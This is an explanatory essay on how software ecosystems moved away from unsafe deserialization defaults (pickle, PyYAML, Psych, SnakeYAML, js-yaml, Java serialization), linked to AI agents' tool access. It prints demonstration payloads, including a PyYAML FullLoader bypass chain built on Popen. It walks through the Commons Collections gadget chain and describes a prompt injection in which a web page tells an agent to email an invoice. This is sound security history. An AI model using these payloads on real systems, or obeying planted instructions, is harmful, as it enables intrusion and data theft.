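# How software ecosystems retired unsafe-by-default interpreters, and what that suggests for AI agents' access to tools

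## How data comes to run as code, and the stages by which a default is changed

Programs constantly save and read data, such as settings, documents and messages from other computers. Reading a file is usually harmless, but several widely used functions will, if the file is written a certain way, run commands chosen by its author with all the permissions of the program that opened it. Security engineers call this arbitrary code execution. Python, Java, PHP, Ruby, JavaScript, .NET and Microsoft Office have all shipped features that allow it. A function is unsafe by default if the shortest or most obvious way to call it lets its input run arbitrary code or commands.

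Over the years the maintainers of these languages and products have restricted some of the functions, removed a few, and left others in place with a warning. Developers of AI agents now face a similar decision about which actions an agent can take without further permission. An agent is a program in which a language model chooses and carries out actions over several steps, such as reading files, running commands or sending email. The older history is useful evidence only if the two situations are similar enough.

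### How a loader becomes an interpreter

An interpreter is a program that reads instructions and carries them out. An eval-style function lets any program use an interpreter to run a string as code. In Python, `eval("2 + 3")` returns 5, but `eval` will also delete files if the string contains code to do that. The danger is at least easy to see, since the function's whole purpose is to run code.

Data running as code is harder to notice in deserialization. Serialization turns an object into bytes or text for storage or sending, and deserialization uses a loader to rebuild the object. A list of numbers is easy to rebuild, but a customer record with its own class (the definition of a type of object and what it can do) is harder because the loader has to use the right class. The format therefore includes the name of the class, which the loader looks up in the running program. Some formats also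 allow a function's name and arguments, because some objects can be rebuilt only by calling a particular function. The serialized data can then contain instructions, and a loader that follows them is an interpreter.

Pickle is Python's built-in format for saving objects. According to Python's *pickle* documentation, a class can define a method called `__reduce__` that returns a function and a set of arguments. On loading, pickle calls the function with those arguments to rebuild the object. The file holds only the function's name, so the loader imports whatever module the name belongs to. By default, it accepts any name.

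The documentation includes a short hand-written example that runs a system command. A milder version, which calls Python's `print` function, looks like this:

```
cbuiltins
print
(S'hello'
tR.
```

The single letters and punctuation marks are instructions for a small machine that keeps its values in a pile. *Security of Python’s pickle and marshal modules* takes apart a stream of the same shape, and the steps are these:

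| In the stream | What the loader does |
|---|---|
| `c`, then `builtins` and `print` | Imports the module `builtins`, finds `print` in it and puts that function on the pile |
| `(` | Puts a marker on the pile |
| `S'hello'` | Puts the text "hello" on the pile |
| `t` | Gathers everything above the marker into one set of arguments |
| `R` | Calls the function with those arguments and puts the result on the pile |
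| `.` | Stops and returns the top of the pile |

A program that passes these bytes to a plain `pickle.loads` call prints "hello", even if the program's own code never mentions `print`. The call returns `None`, Python's empty value, because that is what `print` returns. If the bytes name `os` and `system` instead of `builtins` and `print`, and contain a command instead of "hello", the same six steps run that command on the machine.

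A benign machine-learning model file can look much like a malicious one. *An Empirical Study of Safetensors' Usage Trends and Developers' Perceptions* (Casey, Damian and colleagues, 2025) compares the instructions in one of each. Both files start by looking something up by name. The benign file looks up the model's own class, while the malicious file looks up `exec`, an eval-style function, followed by a command that deletes everything on the machine.

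Now take the same values in JSON, a common text format for exchanging data:

```
{"function": "builtins.print", "arguments": ["hello"]}
```

Python's JSON loader returns a dictionary with two entries and prints nothing. The format has only strings, numbers, true and false, an empty value, lists and name/value pairs. *The JavaScript Object Notation (JSON) Data Interchange Format* (Bray, 2017), the current standard, takes its syntax from JavaScript but leaves out assignment and invocation, so a JSON text cannot express a call. Because of these limits, JSON also cannot restore a customer record as the original object, and the programmer has to write the code that rebuilds it. Pickle rebuilds the object automatically, which is a large part of its appeal.

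Even JSON is only as safe as its loader. Because the syntax comes from JavaScript, that language's `eval` function can read most JSON texts, and for years many web programs used it to do so. A contributor to a mailing-list discussion at the Internet Engineering Task Force, the body that publishes the standard, described the practice as common in browsers (IETF's *Guidance on RFC 4627 as reference* (2012)). An attacker could send JavaScript code instead of valid JSON, and `eval` would run it. Bray's standard calls using `eval` this way generally an unacceptable risk. A program that parses the dictionary above safely can still reintroduce the problem if it then looks up the function named under "function" and calls it.

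### The weakness class and the usual defences

MITRE's *CWE-502*, "Deserialization of Untrusted Data", is an entry in the Common Weakness Enumeration, a public catalogue of software flaws. It covers any product that rebuilds objects from untrusted data without checking well enough that the result is valid. The entry dates from 2006 and appears in every edition of the catalogue's list of the 25 most dangerous weaknesses from 2019 to 2025. It lists Java, Ruby, PHP, Python and JavaScript as affected languages and rates the weakness as often prevalent in AI and machine-learning software.

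In one of MITRE's examples, a server receives a login token, unpickles it, and then checks the signature inside. The check comes too late because an attacker's code runs during the unpickling. Python's maintainers recommend signing pickled data, but a signature protects a program only if the program verifies it before unpickling the data.

Some unsafe loaders don't let the input call a function directly, but will build objects of any class available to the program. To exploit one, an attacker needs a gadget chain, which is a sequence of existing, harmless-looking classes. A crafted object makes the program run their ordinary methods in a combination that does something dangerous. The attacker supplies no new code, and the classes often come from a library that the program's developers installed for some other reason.

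The obvious defence is to limit the names a loader will accept, either with an allowlist, which refuses every name not listed, or with a denylist, which refuses only the names listed. Python's documentation shows a loader with an allowlist of five harmless built-in types. It rejects a stream that references `os.system`, and also one that uses `eval` to reach `os.system` indirectly. A denylist containing only `os.system` would have let the second stream through. MITRE recommends allowlists but warns that they are insufficient alone, because people keep discovering new gadgets. One of its recorded cases is an attack that bypassed the restriction through a class the developers had assumed they could trust.

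Each programmer also has to write more than a dozen lines of code to use the safe loader in Python's documentation, while the unsafe one takes a single call.

### Six stages of retirement

Maintainers who regret an unsafe function cannot simply delete it, because other people's programs depend on it. They have roughly six measures available.

| Stage | What it asks of the maintainer | What it asks of the user |
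|---|---|---|
| Warning in the documentation | Write a paragraph | Find it, and recognise that it applies |
| Safe alternative beside the unsafe call | Build, test and support a second function | Learn that it exists and switch to it |
| Runtime warning | Add a message that appears when the old call runs, and deal with the complaints | Notice the message, then change the call or silence it |
| Default change | Make the plain call the safe one in a new release, and accept that some programs will break | Repair what broke, or ask for the old behaviour explicitly |
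| Removal | Delete the code | Rewrite, or stay on an old release that will stop receiving security fixes |
| Unsafe opt-in | Keep the dangerous behaviour working behind a named setting, argument or package | Type that name and take responsibility for the input |

The stages follow only a loose order. An unsafe opt-in usually arrives with the default change, for users who cannot move yet, and may be removed later. Many functions go through only some of the stages. The pickle module has a prominent warning and a pointer to JSON, but `pickle.loads` still accepts any name. Machine-learning libraries built on pickle have gone further.

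If a user does nothing, the first three stages leave the old program running as before and just as exposed. Changing the default is the first measure that protects this user after an upgrade, but it is also the first that can break the user's program, which partly explains why maintainers put it off.

Warnings do not reach everyone, either. Node.js, which runs JavaScript outside the browser, once had a `Buffer()` function that reserved memory without necessarily clearing it, so leftover data could leak. This danger differs from code execution, but the maintainers retired the function in similar stages. Node.js' *Deprecated APIs* records that they deprecated it in the documentation with version 6. They now offer `Buffer.alloc`, which clears the memory, and `Buffer.allocUnsafe`, which does not and whose name makes the risk easy for reviewers to notice. Version 10 added a runtime warning, but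 by default it appears only for calls in the developer's own code, not for calls inside installed packages.

The same project went further with a function that turns passwords into encryption keys. If the caller didn't specify an algorithm, the function used SHA-1, an old one that the maintainers did not recommend. In version 6 the function printed a warning when the algorithm was left out, and in version 8 it would not run. Callers could still pass an explicit empty value instead of an algorithm until the maintainers closed that gap in version 14.

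Policy partly determines how long all this takes. Python's rules, first drawn up in *PEP 387* (Peterson, 2009), require at least two years of warnings before an incompatible change, and since January 2025 they recommend five. Python's steering council can shorten the period for dangerously insecure features. The maintainers of the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a much younger standard for connecting AI applications to tools, settled in 2026 on a minimum of twelve months, or ninety days where a feature poses an active security risk. In the proposal that set these periods, they argue for runtime warnings because such warnings reach developers who never read the documentation. They concede that people who neither use the official software kits nor read the changelog will still get no warning before a removal.

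### Agents, tool calls and the parallel

A language model on its own produces text. In *MCP 2026 changes the rules*, Granados (2026) describes a model suggesting a list of steps, which the person then carries out one by one. Tools let software carry out the steps instead. The developer gives the model descriptions of certain functions, and the model can answer with a tool call, a structured request for the surrounding software to perform an action, such as reading a file or running a command. The software performs the action and adds the result to the text that the model reads next. An agent repeats this until the task is finished or something stops it.

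MCP is an open standard through which AI applications (clients) connect to programs that offer tools (servers). Anthropic introduced it in 2024. By July 2026, according to the release announcement from the Model Context Protocol (2026) project, developers were downloading its main software kits nearly half a billion times a month. The exchange itself is simple. The client asks the server for its list of tools and receives names, descriptions and the arguments each tool takes. The model picks one. The client then sends a request whose core, in the specification's own example, is this:

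```
{"name": "get_weather", "arguments": {"location": "New York"}}
```

This is plain JSON, and parsing it does nothing. The server then looks up the name and runs the matching function with those arguments.

*Tools* (2026), the part of the Model Context Protocol specification that governs this exchange, describes tools as "model-controlled" and says a human should always be able to deny a call. In standards language, "should" marks a recommendation rather than a requirement, so an application can follow the protocol without ever asking a person to approve a call. The specification's introduction acknowledges that the protocol works through "arbitrary data access and code execution paths".

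Much of what an agent reads comes from strangers. Suppose a user asks for a summary of a web page, and the page contains an instruction to forward the user's latest invoice to some address. The model receives both the request and the page as text. If it then calls the email tool to forward the invoice, the instruction has worked as a prompt injection, which is text in material an agent reads that the model follows as if it were an instruction from its user. Developers have two common defences. An approval prompt asks a person to allow or refuse an action before it runs. A sandbox is an environment in which the operating system or a virtual machine limits which files, networks and processes code can reach.

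In both pickle loading and AI agents' tool use, outside input can select which action runs. A pickle stream specifies a function and its arguments, and the loader calls that function. Similarly, a web page can lead a model to specify a tool and its arguments, which the server then runs.

The routes differ, however. An attacker can name a function directly in a pickle file, and the loader calls it every time. A sentence planted in a web page takes effect only if a model acts on it, and the model can use only the tools that somebody has connected. That list of tools works somewhat like an allowlist, unless one of them runs shell commands, in which case the argument is itself code and the list restricts very little. How far the history of the older functions can guide the defaults for agents depends on how much difference the model makes, and on whether agents can have a safe alternative, as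 pickle users have in JSON.

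## YAML loaders in Python, Ruby, Java and JavaScript

YAML is a text format that people use mostly for settings, because lines such as `port: 8080` are easy to read and write by hand. A YAML file can also contain tags, which tell the loader what kind of value follows. For years, widely used loaders in Python, Ruby, Java and JavaScript accepted tags that let the file choose a class to build or supply code outright. The four groups of maintainers chose different remedies for much the same flaw. Comparing their choices is close to a natural experiment, though not a clean one, because Ruby's loader comes with the language and users install the other three separately.

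### How a tag builds an object

Here is a settings file with one ordinary line and one hostile one, written for PyYAML, the main YAML library for Python:

```
port: 8080
greeting: !!python/object/apply:builtins.print [hello]
```

The tag runs from `!!` to the space. Its first part, `python/object/apply`, is an instruction to call something, `builtins.print` is what to call, and the brackets hold the arguments. A loader that follows the tag calls `print` with "hello", just as pickle does. According to PyYAML, the library's author deliberately made it compatible with pickle. The project's own example of an attack uses the same kind of tag to run a system command.

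PyYAML's safe loader uses a table of supported tags, such as those for text, numbers, lists and name/value pairs. The last entry in the table matches every other tag and raises an error, so the file above would not load at all. This allowlist also rejects harmless data, such as tuples, Python's fixed-length lists, because they have their own tag.

The other languages differ in how much work the attacker must do. In Ruby, a tag names a class, and the loader creates an object of that class and fills in its contents. The attacker then needs a gadget chain. The documentation of SafeYAML, a Ruby add-on, demonstrates one using a class that pastes names from the data into Ruby source code. If a name contains text that closes the current method and then adds a command, Ruby executes the command. In Java, a tag names a class and can pass arguments to its constructor, the code that sets up a new object.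 In JavaScript, the tag `!!js/function` held the source text of a function. The loader did not call the function, but an attacker could store it under the name `toString`, which JavaScript calls automatically whenever a program converts the object to text.

### PyYAML withdraws a safe default after two days

PyYAML's first release, in May 2006, had both `load` and `safe_load`. Its documentation warned in bold type against using `load` on untrusted data. Nemec's Red Hat bug report, *CVE-2017-18342 PyYAML* (2018), quotes the warning, which says `yaml.load` is "as powerful as pickle.load". PyYAML thus began with the first two of the six stages in place and went no further for twelve years.

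In June 2018 the project released version 4.1, in which `load` behaved like `safe_load` and a new function, `danger_load`, kept the old behaviour. That same day, Gaynor (2018), in *CVE for PyYAML RCE-factory API*, asked for a CVE, a numbered entry in the public catalogue of specific vulnerabilities. Gaynor based the request on the degree to which `load` had been a "footgun", a programmers' word for a feature that makes it easy for users to hurt themselves, rather than on a new bug. The entry became CVE-2017-18342.

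Two days after the release, the lead maintainer withdrew it. The notice by Ingy dot Net (2018), in *[ANN] PyYAML-4.1* mentions only "too many problems". The same maintainer gave a fuller account the next day in *PyYAML 4.2 Release Plan* (ingydotnet, 2018). The team had rushed out 4.1 because the previous version did not work with the new Python 3.7, but then could not build the packages that Windows users needed. Reports of other faults were coming in. The lead maintainer had learned only after the release that it contained the new default.

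The packaging trouble would have forced 4.1's withdrawal anyway, but the next version did not restore the safe default. The lead maintainer agreed with its purpose but objected that it would break a great deal of existing code to provide something `safe_load` had always offered. The maintainer also found the name `danger_load` misleading for programs that read only their own files, where the plain function might be "a big can of gasoline, but nothing's on fire". In PyYAML's discussion of the reversal, a co-maintainer disagreed, arguing that Python users had clearly asked for a library that did not run code by default. The co-maintainer then left the project, complaining that one person had to approve everything.

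The CVE still stood after the release meant to fix it was withdrawn. GitHub, which hosts most open-source projects, began sending automatic alerts to projects that used PyYAML when the only fixes available were test versions. Users in the PyYAML discussion *Security fixe reported by github* disagreed about whether there was a flaw at all. When one asked how developers were supposed to know about the danger, another answered that it was in the manual. A third compared the old default to a car with its seatbelt sensor switched off.

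Linux distributors were also unsure how to treat CVE-2017-18342. Red Hat lowered its severity to moderate because people had known about the behaviour for so long, and noted that the checking tool Bandit had flagged it for over three years. *CVE-2017-18342 status*, a thread started by Jwomers (2018), quotes Debian's view that this was a "well-known design deficiency" and that the CVE was meant to raise awareness. Yet Red Hat's *CVE-2017-18342* now gives the flaw a score of 9.8 out of 10.

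### FullLoader, the halfway default

The PyYAML maintainers still considered it infeasible to make `load` behave like `safe_load`, so in version 5.1, released on 13 March 2019, a plain call to `load` printed a warning and used a new loader called FullLoader. *Deprecate/warn usage of yaml.load(input)*, the change that introduced FullLoader, describes it as avoiding all known ways of executing code while reading almost everything the old loader could. The change also announces that calling `load` without naming a loader will become an error in "a future release", with no date.

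FullLoader added two checks. It would use a module only if the program had already imported it, and if a tag created an object, the name in the tag had to refer to a class, not an ordinary function. Shortly before the release, a maintainer acknowledged in the Jwomers thread that creating an object still runs the class's setup code, which "may be exploitable", but promised in the same passage that a plain `load` could no longer run arbitrary code.

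Attackers had three ways around the checks within sixteen months. Averlon's *CVE-2019-20477* describes the first, which used `Popen`, a class in Python's standard module for starting other programs. The checks allowed `Popen` because it is a class, and creating a `Popen` object starts a command. To block this, version 5.2 removed the `apply` tag from FullLoader, but it kept a similar tag, `new`, which creates an object without running its usual set-up code.

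The second route went through `new`. After creating an object, FullLoader let the file set the object's attributes and then called the object's `extend` method to add list items. An attacker could replace `extend` with a function they chose, and the loader would call it. *Prevents arbitrary code execution during python/object/new constructor* (ret2libc, 2020) fixed this with a denylist that blocked the name `extend` and every name that starts and ends with two underscores.

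Four months later a user posted several ways around the denylist. Lightrun's *load() and FullLoader still vulnerable to fairly trivial RCE*, a copy of the discussion, includes another, from a different participant, which nests four `new` tags inside one another. Written as ordinary Python, it amounts to this:

```
tuple(map(type(Popen.__new__(Popen)), ["ls"]))
```

It is easiest to read from the inside out:

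1. `Popen.__new__(Popen)` creates an empty `Popen` object, which starts nothing.
2. `type` takes that object and returns its class, so the file now holds `Popen` itself.
3. `map` prepares to apply `Popen` to each item in a list whose only item is the command `ls`.
4. `tuple` collects the results, which makes `map` do its work, and the command runs.

`Popen`, `type`, `map` and `tuple` are all classes in Python 3, so they pass FullLoader's check. The gadget chain is built almost entirely from parts that every Python program has. PyYAML's *CHANGES* records that version 5.4 moved the tags for arbitrary Python objects out of FullLoader in January 2021, by which time the project had largely abandoned the idea of a loader that was both complete and safe.

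FullLoader, the halfway default, failed mainly because its maintainers designed it to block the attacks they knew about, so each fix stopped one attack and left attackers free to look for another. SafeLoader avoided this problem by using an allowlist.

PyYAML's page told programmers that the best way to silence the warning was to name a loader, and it gave `Loader=yaml.FullLoader` as the example, so anyone who followed it wrote the flawed loader into their own code. The same page later told readers to avoid FullLoader for now. Many people would never have seen the warning, because web server developers often do not look at the output where it appears, according to the documentation of PyCharm Security, a code-checking plugin.

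A participant in the discussion that Lightrun copied did a quick search of public code on GitHub and found about 762,000 files that used PyYAML. Up to 529,000 of them relied on the default loader, 220,000 used the safe one, and 13,000 explicitly used the unsafe one. More than those 13,000 may have needed the unsafe behaviour, because before 2019 a programmer could get it just by calling `load`. Many of the 529,000 files presumably read only the program's own settings. Still, after fourteen years of warnings in bold type, most callers used the short name, and the participant thought they expected `yaml.load` to be as harmless as `json.load`.

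### Making the caller choose

In September 2020 the lead maintainer proposed switching the default to SafeLoader in a later release. Instead, PyYAML 6.0, announced in October 2021, made `load` fail when called without a named loader (Ingy dot Net (2021), in *[ANN] PyYAML-6.0 Released*).

Programs broke at once, including those that had only read harmless files. Glusto, a testing tool, went back to PyYAML 5.4.1 because changing its own code would have needed more testing. Users of Google Colab, an online notebook service, found that a charting package no longer imported. In PyYAML's discussion of the breakage, a maintainer said that there had been prominent warnings for years and that moving people to a much less capable loader would have been just as big a break. One user later objected that breaking all the old code was worse than breaking the half a percent that relied on unsafe features.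 That figure was a guess, but the argument is fair, because a safe default would have kept most of these programs running and made them more secure.

The maintainers' choice does have one practical advantage. A missing argument causes an error the first time the line runs, probably on the developer's own machine. A program switched silently to the safe loader fails only when it loads a file containing a tag, which might be months later at a customer's site.

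Programmers who are required to name a loader can still choose an unsafe one. PyYAML kept its original loader under its original name for compatibility, so `Loader=yaml.Loader` satisfies the new requirement and fully restores the unsafe behaviour. The blog post *yaml and python structures* describes how its writer passed `yaml.Loader` to read a file containing tuples, and only afterwards discovered that the program would now run code from any file it loaded.

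### Ruby learns from Rails

Ruby had a much more serious problem. On 8 January 2013, Patterson (2013), a maintainer of the website framework Ruby on Rails, announced in *Multiple vulnerabilities in parameter parsing in Action Pack (CVE-2013-0156)* that every version of Rails let attackers run code on the server. Rails accepted form data in several formats, including XML, and an XML value could declare its own type. YAML was one of the permitted types, so an attacker could put a YAML document inside an XML request and Rails would load it, including its tags.

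A Rails site could be exposed even if its developers had never written a line that mentioned YAML. XML support was on by default, and according to Insinuator's *Analysis of Rails XML Parameter Parsing Vulnerability* (2013), many Rails developers did not seem to know it existed. A warning in the YAML loader's documentation could not have helped them. Patterson told everyone to upgrade immediately or turn off XML support.

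Ruby's loader, Psych, had no safe alternative to `YAML.load`. The day after the announcement, Sawyer (2013) asked for one in *YAML load mode that does instantiate Ruby* (the title is missing a "not", as Sawyer later pointed out). A wiki program Sawyer had contributed to had just disabled a feature because it relied on `YAML.load`. Patterson, who also maintained Psych, replied that `YAML.load` enables remote code execution only when combined with some other object that does something dangerous. That was accurate, but Rails contained such an object. Patterson added `safe_load` to Psych that May.

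For eight years, Psych offered both the unsafe `load` and the safer `safe_load`. In May 2021, Patterson (2021), in *[ruby/psych] Use Psych.safe_load by default*, made safe loading the default, explaining that "too many applications make the mistake" of using `load` on untrusted data. Psych 4.0 kept the old behaviour as `unsafe_load`. PyYAML had withdrawn essentially the same change three years earlier.

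Psych 4.0.0 broke a good deal of existing software. Shibata, in *Incompatible changes with Psych 4.0.0*, reported trouble with stored configuration and with Ruby's own packaging data. Rails failed on the standard database configuration file for new applications. Within days, Boussier (2021), in *Fix ruby-master test suite (Psych 4.0.0)*, changed 18 files in Rails so that it loaded trusted YAML with `unsafe_load`. Redmine, a project-management program, could no longer read some of its saved settings, and Maeda (2021), in *Psych 4*, also fixed this with `unsafe_load`. Ezr, in *Pin psych < 4*, instead kept Foreman, which manages fleets of servers, on the old version as an "easy workaround" until the team could repair its test data.

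Switching to `unsafe_load` is better than pinning the old version. Redmine is no safer than before where it calls `unsafe_load`, but a reviewer can now find the word "unsafe" in the source code, and the program's other calls to `load` become safe. A project that pins the old version keeps the old behavior for every call to `load`.

The database file failed because it used aliases, a YAML feature unrelated to classes. Aliases let a writer label part of a file, for example with `&default`, and repeat it elsewhere with `*default`. Rails used them to share settings between the development and live versions of a site. The safe loader refused aliases, and in the discussion that Shibata opened, Takashi Kokubun asked why `load` should refuse them too if the purpose was to stop files from creating arbitrary objects. Patterson gave the example of a list that contains itself, which can be written in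 two lines of YAML with an alias. Psych loads the list without trouble, but a program that walks through it never reaches the end. Patterson still leaned towards allowing aliases, since such attacks had only been theoretical, but admitted to being "very tired of dealing with YAML related security issues". In the released version, callers have to enable aliases explicitly.

The maintainers also blocked aliases, which made the change more disruptive than it had to be to address the main danger. A Rails user with an ordinary settings file got an error that had nothing to do with running code.

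Yui Naruse argued for keeping Ruby 3.1 compatible with 3.0 and opposed including Psych 4. Another participant, Carsten Bormann, observed that leaving it out would make little difference, because users would get the new Psych with their next routine package update anyway. The team shipped Psych 4 with Ruby 3.1 and a note in the release news. Ctrl.blog's *Ruby 3.1’s incompatible changes to its YAML module (Psych 4)* considered that insufficient. It agreed with the new default but complained that Psych had never printed a warning, so most developers would learn of the change when their programs stopped. Even loading a date now caused an error unless the program listed the `Date` class as permitted.

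### SnakeYAML and the documented feature

The argument over whether a documented danger counts as a vulnerability was sharpest in Java. In December 2022 the main Java library, SnakeYAML, received CVE-2022-1471, with the same 9.8 score. GitLab's *CVE-2022-1471* (2022) gives the line of code at issue:

```
new Yaml(new Constructor(TestDataClass.class)).load(yamlContent);
```

Even with this in place, a tag deeper in the file could name any class, though a programmer might well expect the file to produce only a `TestDataClass`. SnakeYAML raised an error when the object was of the wrong type, but only after building it, so the check came too late, as it did in MITRE's example of the login token. CIRCL's *GHSA-mjmj-j48q-9wg2*, a copy of Google's advisory on the flaw, contains the output of a test attack. The program reports the error, and a test server's log shows the web request that the attack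 was designed to make.

Snyk's *Arbitrary Code Execution Affecting org.yaml:snakeyaml package, versions [0,2.0)* (2022) reports that SnakeYAML's maintainers disputed the risk, arguing that an attack requires that the application already trusts the source of the YAML, or that someone has already compromised it. The CVE recommended using the library's safe alternative, `SafeConstructor`. SnakeYAML's wiki page *Spring and CVE-2022-1471* told users of Spring, a popular Java framework, that Spring already used `SafeConstructor` together with an allowlist of classes. It advised anyone whose security scanner still flagged the library to report a false positive to the makers of their "low quality tooling".

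The maintainers had a point about Spring, because a scanner that looks only at version numbers can't detect whether a program calls the library safely. But their general defence, that the behaviour is by design and users are responsible for the input, is weaker here than it was for PyYAML, whose documentation told users plainly what `load` could do. A Java programmer who had named the expected class had some reason to think the call was safe. The same defence has since come up over how MCP clients launch local servers.

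In the end, scanners did more than the argument to drive upgrades. *Upgrade to SnakeYaml 2.2 and use SafeConstructor to mitigate CVE-2022-1471*, a note from the modelling platform Simantics, says that `SafeConstructor` protected the platform even on the old version, but that it had to upgrade anyway because scanners would go on flagging every 1.x release. SnakeYAML 2.0, released in early 2023, made the safe behaviour the default, and the Simantics note says most code should need no changes. But Ubuntu's *CVE-2022-1471* (2022) lists the package in the 2024 long-term release as unfixed, on the grounds that backporting the fix was infeasible.

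### js-yaml, and the four compared

The JavaScript library js-yaml made `load` safe by default in version 4.0, released in January 2021. Until then, `load` had accepted the function tag and `safeLoad` had refused it. The maintainers moved the JavaScript-specific tags to a separate package and removed `safeLoad`. Programs that still call `safeLoad` get an error message that `load` is now safe and should be used instead. The change therefore broke programs that had taken the precaution of using `safeLoad`, while those that had used `load` on plain files kept working and became safe without modification.

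| | PyYAML | Psych (Ruby) | SnakeYAML (Java) | js-yaml |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Plain call today | Fails unless the caller names a loader | Safe | Safe | Safe |
| Unsafe opt-in | `unsafe_load`, but also the innocent-looking `yaml.Loader` | `unsafe_load` | Explicit settings that permit classes | A separate package |
| How users learned of the change | Runtime warning for two years and seven months, then an error | Failing programs and a release note | Alerts from security scanners | An error naming the replacement |
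| What broke | Every call without a named loader | Files with dates, aliases or custom classes | Programs that relied on custom classes | Calls to `safeLoad` |
| Who pushed | Outside developers, a co-maintainer and GitHub's alerts | The maintainer who had handled the Rails emergency | Outside security researchers and scanners | The library's own maintainers |

PyYAML gave the longest warning but still broke the most code, because its warning period ended in an error instead of a safe default. Psych gave no warning, and the worst of the damage to Rails took only days to repair. Warnings are still useful. Ctrl.blog's complaint was reasonable, and a year of messages would have spared the Redmine and Foreman developers a surprise. But a warning period does little good if the new behaviour is badly chosen or the recommended loader turns out to be unsafe.

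Some users have good reason not to use the safe call. MkDocs, a documentation site generator, has its own loader, and its maintainers explain in a discussion on the project's tracker that they decided the benefits of avoiding the "safe" version outweighed the risks for their purposes. All four libraries left such users a way to continue loading YAML unsafely.

Because the short name now refers to the safe loader, `YAML.load` in Ruby and `load` in js-yaml are safe or dangerous depending on the installed version of the library, and a reviewer cannot tell which from the line of code alone. PyYAML's users avoid this problem with `safe_load`, which has meant the same thing since 2006.

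## Built-in object serialization in Java and .NET

Java and .NET both shipped with a built-in, general-purpose object serializer, Java in 1997 and .NET in 2002. In both formats, as with PyYAML's tags, the incoming data specifies which types to build. Microsoft removed its serializer, BinaryFormatter, from the current line of .NET in 2024. Oracle, which leads Java's development, considers Java's serializer a mistake but still ships it enabled by default.

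### How Java rebuilds an object

A Java programmer makes a class serializable by adding the words `implements Serializable` to its definition. A program that receives an order from another machine can then rebuild it with one line:

```
Order order = (Order) in.readObject();
```

The `readObject` call reads a class name from the stream, finds that class, creates an object without running the class's constructor, and fills in the fields. The `(Order)` cast checks the object's type only after these steps, so if the stream contains the name of some other class, Java builds that object before the cast fails. The same late check caught SnakeYAML users off guard.

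Skipping the constructor also causes problems, because programmers put their validity checks there. *Towards Better Serialization*, a design note from OpenJDK, the open-source project that develops Java, includes a `Range` class whose constructor rejects a lower bound above the upper one. Under the existing mechanism, a crafted stream could still produce a range from 5 to 1. The note calls serialization "an invisible but public constructor". It also acknowledges that Java would probably not have become dominant without the feature, which let programs send whole objects between machines with almost no extra code.

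A malformed range is still only bad data. To run code, an attacker needs classes that run their own methods while Java rebuilds their objects, and many classes have to do this. *Sleeping Giants* (Kreyssig, Riom et al., 2025) gives the example of a hash table, which stores each entry at a position calculated from its key. The positions can differ between machines, so the table recalculates them on loading by calling a method on every key. The attacker chooses the keys, and therefore which class's version of that method runs.

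### The 2015 gadget chains

In January 2015 the security researchers Gabriel Lawrence and Chris Frohoff gave a talk on attacks of this kind, and Frohoff published a tool, ysoserial, that generates the malicious streams. The best-known chain used Commons Collections, a popular library of data structures from the Apache Software Foundation. Sayar, Bartel and colleagues (2022), in *An In-depth Study of Java Deserialization Remote-Code Execution Exploits and Vulnerabilities*, trace it call by call. Somewhat simplified, it runs like this:

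1. The stream names `AnnotationInvocationHandler`, a class in Java's own library. While Java rebuilds this object, the object asks a map (a table of names and values) for its entries.
2. The attacker has supplied a proxy in place of an ordinary map. A proxy passes every request to a handler, which here looks up a value in another map.
3. That map is a `LazyMap` from Commons Collections. When a value is missing, a `LazyMap` creates it by running a "transformer", a small object that turns one value into another.
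4. The attacker has supplied a series of transformers. One type, `InvokerTransformer`, calls whatever method its data names, and the series ends by calling `Runtime.exec`, which runs a system command.

The vulnerable program only needs to have Commons Collections on its classpath, the set of code that Java can load for it, and doesn't have to use the library.

The talk at first had little effect on vendors. In November 2015 Stephen Breen of Foxglove Security published attacks on the five products named in the title of *What Do WebLogic, WebSphere, JBoss, Jenkins, OpenNMS, and Your Application Have in Common?* (@breenmachine, 2015). Neither the products nor the Commons Collections library had a patch, although the example code had been public for more than nine months. Eckenfels and Gregory, in *Apache Commons statement to widespread Java object de-serialisation vulnerability*, explain that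 the original researchers had seen no need to alert the library's maintainers, because fixing one library would only start a game of "Whack-a-Mole". The maintainers disabled deserialization of the dangerous class anyway, and warned that a program using the new version would still be open to attack through other classes. The CERT Coordination Center, in *Apache Commons Collections Java library insecurely deserializes data* (2015), told developers that it knew of no full solution and that they would need to redesign their applications.

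According to Sayar and colleagues, an attacker took control of 2,000 computers at San Francisco's transport agency in 2016 through a Java deserialization vulnerability in a web server.

The same study shows how slowly libraries removed their gadgets. It tested 19 published attacks against many versions of the libraries involved, and found that removal took between several months and almost twelve years, and almost six years on average. It found no patch for 37.5% of the libraries. A gadget does no harm until some program deserializes untrusted data, and a maintainer can reasonably consider that the program's fault. But the program's developers may not know the gadget is there.

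Of the 58 vulnerabilities that the researchers could analyse, application developers fixed 11 by disabling deserialization, 11 by adding an allowlist and 10 by adding a denylist. For 13 of the 58, vendors left the code unchanged and offered only a workaround, such as blocking a network port. The developers of Atlassian's build server Bamboo responded to one vulnerability by upgrading a library. The upgrade did not prevent the next vulnerability, after which they added lists of permitted and forbidden classes.

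### JEP 290, a filter that starts out empty

In April 2016, OpenJDK's *JEP 290* (2016), a JDK Enhancement Proposal, proposed a general defence for Java in the form of a filter that inspects a stream as Java reads it. The filter was due in Java 9, but InfoQ's *Object Deserialisation Filters Backported from Java 9* reports that Oracle also added it to Java 6, 7 and 8.

With a filter in place, deserialization works as follows:

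1. Java reads the class name of the next object and, before creating the object, passes the class to the filter. It skips this step for plain numbers and text.
2. If the object is an array, Java also passes its length. If the stream points back to an earlier object, Java calls the filter again so that it can check the running totals.
3. The filter answers that the item is allowed, rejected or undecided.
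4. If the item is rejected, Java stops with an error. Otherwise it builds the object and moves on to the next.

Unlike the cast to `Order`, this check runs early enough to block an attack. The filter can also enforce four limits: `maxdepth` on nesting depth, `maxrefs` on the number of internal references, `maxbytes` on stream length, and `maxarray` on array size. These help against streams designed to exhaust the machine's memory. A gadget chain can be quite short, so stopping one depends mostly on the class rules.

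The simplest way to set up a filter is a line of patterns that Java reads from left to right. A program that only needs to receive orders could use this one:

```
jdk.serialFilter=maxarray=1000;com.example.orders.*;!*
```

The middle pattern accepts any class in the `com.example.orders` package. An exclamation mark means "reject", and an asterisk on its own matches everything, so the last pattern rejects whatever the middle one did not accept.

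| Next item in the stream | What happens |
|---|---|
| An `Order` from `com.example.orders` | Allowed by the middle pattern |
| The customer's name, as plain text | Java does not call the filter |
| An array of 5,000 orders | Rejected, because Java checks limits before classes |
| `AnnotationInvocationHandler`, the start of the chain above | Rejected by `!*` before Java creates the object |

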